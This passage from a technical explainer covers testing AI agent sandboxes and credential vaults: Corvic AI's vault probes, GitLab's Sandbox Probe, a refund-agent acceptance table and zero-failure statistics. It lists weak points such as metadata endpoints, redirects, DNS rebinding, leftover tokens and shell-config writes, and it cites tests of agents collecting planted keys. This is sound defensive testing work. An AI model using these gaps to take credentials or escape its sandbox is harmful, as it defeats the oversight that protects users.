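Kenney and colleagues used both kinds of control when they tested Corvic AI's vault on 27 September 2026. They ran two experiments in the company's Python sandbox, giving the code only a FRED connector in the first and only a GitHub connector in the second. A connector is the vault's record of a service and its key. The team set the expected result of each test, or probe, before running it.

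Five of the 16 probes tested whether the vault tied each key to its own host, and one tested whether a permitted call worked. The other ten covered environment variables, mounted files, disclosure to other servers, the key's visibility to the code, and cloud metadata, with two probes for each. All 16 gave the expected security result.

The positive control was a request to GitHub for the logged-in user's details. The code sent no key, but GitHub returned a 200 and an account's identity, so the vault must have added the key. The code also inspected a GitHub request before sending it and found no Authorization header.

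The code then searched for the key. It found 20 environment variables, none with a suspicious name or a value in a known key format. It could read the file where Linux lists a process's environment variables, but found no key there. None of 12 common credential files existed, and a search for mounted secrets found nothing.

Three echo services, which return the headers they receive, showed no key. In both experiments, OpenAI's API replied that the request had no authentication, even while the GitHub connector was attached. Requests to Google's and Amazon's cloud metadata services timed out after six seconds. The echo services had replied normally, so a dead network can't explain these results.

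The FRED connector disclosed nothing, but it didn't work either, because the vault's settings put the key in the wrong place. Kenney and colleagues scored function and security separately, so this failure doesn't change the security score of 16 out of 16. It does weaken the first experiment, because FRED's error message doesn't show whether the vault attached the key at all, and a vault that never attached keys would have passed the same leak tests. The GitHub experiment is better evidence, because the key worked at its own host and did not appear at any other host the team tried.

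The team tested its own company's product with a small set of probes it chose itself. It did not repeat the trials or send many requests at once. It also did not test redirects, a hostile server at a permitted address, or DNS rebinding, in which the owner of a domain name changes the address it points to after a proxy has checked it. The search for keys relied on known formats and could have missed keys in other formats. The timeouts show only that the code couldn't reach the metadata services during those runs.

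Kenney and colleagues consider a prompt injection benchmark the most valuable next test, because it would measure the remaining risk that their threat scores only estimate. Baya's developers ran such a benchmark, WASP, on their own system.

### GitLab's test for a missing sandbox

If the sandbox for a GitLab job can't start, the job runs without one unless an administrator has turned on the setting that prevents this. To detect a missing sandbox, GitLab offers Sandbox Probe, an agent job that tests its own restrictions and prints the evidence.

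In this job, the agent only runs two fixed scripts and posts their output, so it makes no judgements. One script compares the expected and actual result of each check, and the other prints the raw output of the commands.

The report begins with either "Sandbox: ACTIVE" or "Sandbox: NOT ACTIVE". It shows ACTIVE only if the sandbox's settings exist and an attempt to write outside the permitted folders has failed. GitLab's default image runs as root, which ordinary file permissions don't restrict, so the sandbox is the likely reason for the failure.

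The script makes 14 checks. Some compare the settings in force with the expected ones, some try to write to permitted and protected folders, and the rest contact five domains. The table shows the results when projects could add their own domains to the group's list. The last two columns, which are not from GitLab's tests, show what should happen on a machine with ordinary internet access but no sandbox, and in a sandbox with no network.

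| Domain | Rule | With the sandbox | No sandbox | No network |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| gitlab.com | Always permitted | Reached | Reached | Failed |
| registry.npmjs.org | Recommended by GitLab | Reached | Reached | Failed |
| example.com | Permitted by the project | Reached | Reached | Failed |
| pypi.org | Recommended, but denied by the project | Blocked | Reached | Failed |
| httpbin.org | On no list | Blocked | Reached | Failed |

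The test needs both groups of domains, because the first three would be reachable without a sandbox and the last two would be unreachable without a network. In strict mode, where projects can't add domains, the sandbox also blocked example.com. All 14 checks gave the expected results in both modes on 16 October 2026. On 17 November, GitLab reran the flexible mode with a new version that added the ACTIVE line, and all 14 checks again gave the expected results.

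The proxy returned `blocked-by-allowlist` for both blocked domains, even though the project's denylist blocked pypi.org. The network checks therefore show only that a request failed, and the settings checks have to establish which rule stopped it.

The probe also has gaps. The default image has no `~/.ssh` folder, so the script can't test the rule that hides it. Traffic to local and private addresses doesn't pass through the proxy, so the probe doesn't cover the cloud metadata address. Code in a job that passes all 14 checks can still read a credential, because GitLab's own tokens remain in the environment.

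### An acceptance table for the shop

*AI Sandboxes* (2026) argues that controls reduce risk only when there is evidence that they are configured and active. The tests below would provide that evidence for the shop. The builder runs them on a copy of the system with test keys and invented orders, including WEB-1042 and POS-1042. Stand-ins replace the shop platform and the chat service, so no money moves and the builder can simulate a failure in either service.

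| Area | Test | Expected result | Sign of failure |
|---|---|---|---|
| Isolation | One program leaves a marker in memory. The next looks for the marker, files and keys, then adds two numbers | It finds nothing and returns the sum | It finds something, or returns no sum |
| Network | Request the order list, then the recording server by name and by IP address | The orders arrive, and the server records nothing | The server records a request, or no orders arrive |
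| Credentials | Both stand-ins record the headers they receive and repeat them in their replies | Each call arrives with its own key, and the program sees `[removed]` | A call arrives with the wrong key or none, or the program sees a key |
| Permission rules | Request the correct refund. In separate runs, request one for POS-1042, one that is a cent too high and one with an extra field | Only the correct refund reaches the owner's dialog | Another refund reaches it, or the correct one doesn't |
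| Approval | While the $38 dialog is open, request $35 from a new run. Then approve the first dialog twice | The platform records one refund of $38, and the $35 request gets its own dialog | The platform records $35, two refunds or none |
| Stored code | Add a space to the stored program and run it, then remove the space and run it again | The launcher refuses the first run and allows the second | It allows both or refuses both |
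| Changed API field | The chat stand-in starts to require `message` instead of `text` | The launcher suspends the program and names the field. After an approved repair, the message arrives and there is still one refund | The run reports success without a message, or the repair causes a second refund |
| Timeout after a write | The shop stand-in records the refund and drops the connection. In another run, it drops the first request before recording it | Each run ends with one refund | The first run ends with two, or the second with none |
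| Logs | An error reply contains a dummy key and a request number | The log contains the number but not the key | A search finds the key, or the number is missing |

Every row includes a case that should succeed. For example, a gateway that never retried a refund would pass the first timeout test but fail the second, because the customer would not get the refund. The stand-in must handle idempotency keys as the real platform does, or the test result will be wrong.

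Some test values must get past other controls to reach the ones being tested. The approval test uses $35 because the gateway's limit would refuse $380 even if the dialog were broken. The chat stand-in changes its behaviour but not its published description, because the launcher would detect a new description before the run and the test would never reach the later checks.

Planted keys make leaks easier to find because the builder knows what to search for. *AI Safety Requires Effective Controllability* (2026) describes experiments in which each agent's container held invented cloud keys, passwords and a fake private key, to test whether the agent would try to collect them. The shop's dummy keys should have the same format as its real ones. The builder should plant one key that is stored in the gateway and one that has never been stored there, then search the logs, saved conversations and the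 model's input for both, in plain text and in base64.

The builder can also have the shop stand-in redirect a request to the recording server, to test redirects, which Kenney and colleagues left out. The gateway should return the redirect to the program and refuse the request that follows. DNS rebinding matters less for the shop because the gateway contacts only two domain names, and an attacker controls neither.

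A sandbox on a laptop needs more isolation tests. *Lessons from Penetration Tests on Large-Scale Agent Systems* (2026) examined two agent systems, and in both, agents could run any code with access to the whole file system and the outside network. NVIDIA considers it mandatory to block writes outside the workspace and to the agent's configuration files. A test program could try to change `~/.zshrc`, which runs whenever the user opens a zsh terminal. It should try this directly and then through a second program that it starts.

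The builder should also test what happens when a control breaks. According to GitLab's *Agent tool governance*, an agent receives no tools if the service that looks up its permission rules has a persistent error. In the shop, the builder can turn off the data store that counts refunds and check that the gateway refuses every refund. The builder can then turn it back on and check that the correct refund works.

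### What a clean result proves

A system that passes every test may still fail sometimes. Statistics can limit how often, but only for a particular kind of test. Suppose each of *n* independent trials has the same unknown probability *p* of failure. The chance of seeing no failures is (1 − *p*)^*n*. The 95% upper bound is the value of *p* that makes this chance 5%:

```
(1 - p)^n = 0.05
p = 1 - 0.05^(1/n)        roughly 3/n when n is above 30
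```

With 16 trials and no failures, the exact 95% upper confidence bound on the failure rate is 17%. (The approximation 3/n, where n is the number of trials, gives 19%.) Lowering the bound to 1% takes about 300 trials without a failure.

Carter and Woolson (2004) derive this formula in *Statistical design considerations for pilot studies transitioning therapies from the bench* and warn against calling a treatment harmless just because a small trial found no harm. *Systematic reviews of adverse effects* adds that readers should ask how thoroughly the researchers looked for harm. For a search of the shop's logs, that means asking which key formats the scanner recognises.

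The vault's 16 probes don't support even the 17% figure. Kenney and colleagues acknowledge that no confidence interval would be meaningful. The formula assumes that every trial has the same chance of failure, but the probes have no common failure rate, because reading an environment variable and contacting an echo service test different things. The probes also aren't independent, since if the vault had attached its key to every request, all three echo services would have revealed the same fault.

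Attackers also don't choose their methods at random. If the vault leaked keys through redirects, an attacker who found the leak could use it every time. Running the same 16 probes a hundred times would give 1,600 passes and an apparent bound of 0.2%, but redirects would still be untested.

The formula is more useful when chance affects the result, such as when measuring how often a model writes a program that picks the wrong order. The builder could have the model write 300 programs for randomly generated test shops. If none picked the wrong order, the builder could be 95% confident that the rate was below about 1% for that model and similar shops. This would cost $210 at Baya's average of $0.70 per task. The shop's monthly runs would take 25 years to provide as many trials.

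### When to test again

A test result applies only to the version tested, and an ordinary update can change what a sandbox permits. GitLab's *Allow /tmp writes in the SRT sandbox for Duo Workflow* describes an update that let agents write almost anywhere in the temporary folder `/tmp`, where they had been limited to one subfolder. GitLab made the change because models naturally use `/tmp` for scratch files. Anyone who relied on the old limit to protect other files in that folder would have needed to test again.

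Updates can also stop a system from working. GitLab's *Duo Agent Platform workflows fail to start* (2026) reports that on 3 June a change to the default configuration prevented some sandboxed jobs from starting. A job that never starts leaks nothing, so only a positive control, which checks that permitted actions succeed, would have detected the problem.

For the shop, the builder can match the tests to the change:

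| Change | Tests to repeat |
|---|---|
| Sandbox version or settings | Isolation and network |
| Gateway code or allowlist | The whole table |
| New key or new permissions for a key | Credentials, plus one call that the key should not allow |
| New version of an API | Credentials, permission rules, changed field and timeout |
| New or repaired stored program | The admission check, stored code and permission rules |
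| New log format or logging tool | Logs |
| New model | The owner's ordinary request and prompt injection tests |

The gateway's rules don't depend on the model, but a new model may write programs that the rules wrongly block, or that bypass them in a way the old model never used.

Hosted services can change without notice, which is another reason for the launcher to test the boundary before each run. *Parallax* (2026) describes a system that does not start if such a test fails. The system also checks whether the agent's process can access the process that controls it. *RecreationWorld* (2026), a set of test environments for agents, stops a run if it can't install the network rules. It also probes raw IP addresses, which can reveal an open route even when name lookups don't work.

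The open-source project claude-sandbox automates a longer set of tests. Its *Verification checks* describes a command that runs 18 pass-or-fail checks and, if they all pass, makes 10 attempts to break out of the sandbox. The command returns an error if any test fails, so a developer can run it automatically after every change.

Before each monthly task, the shop's launcher can run the two-request program against the real gateway, because the program only reads orders and contacts the builder's own server. The builder can run the other tests in the table on the test copy the day before, which leaves time to fix any faults before the owner asks for another refund.
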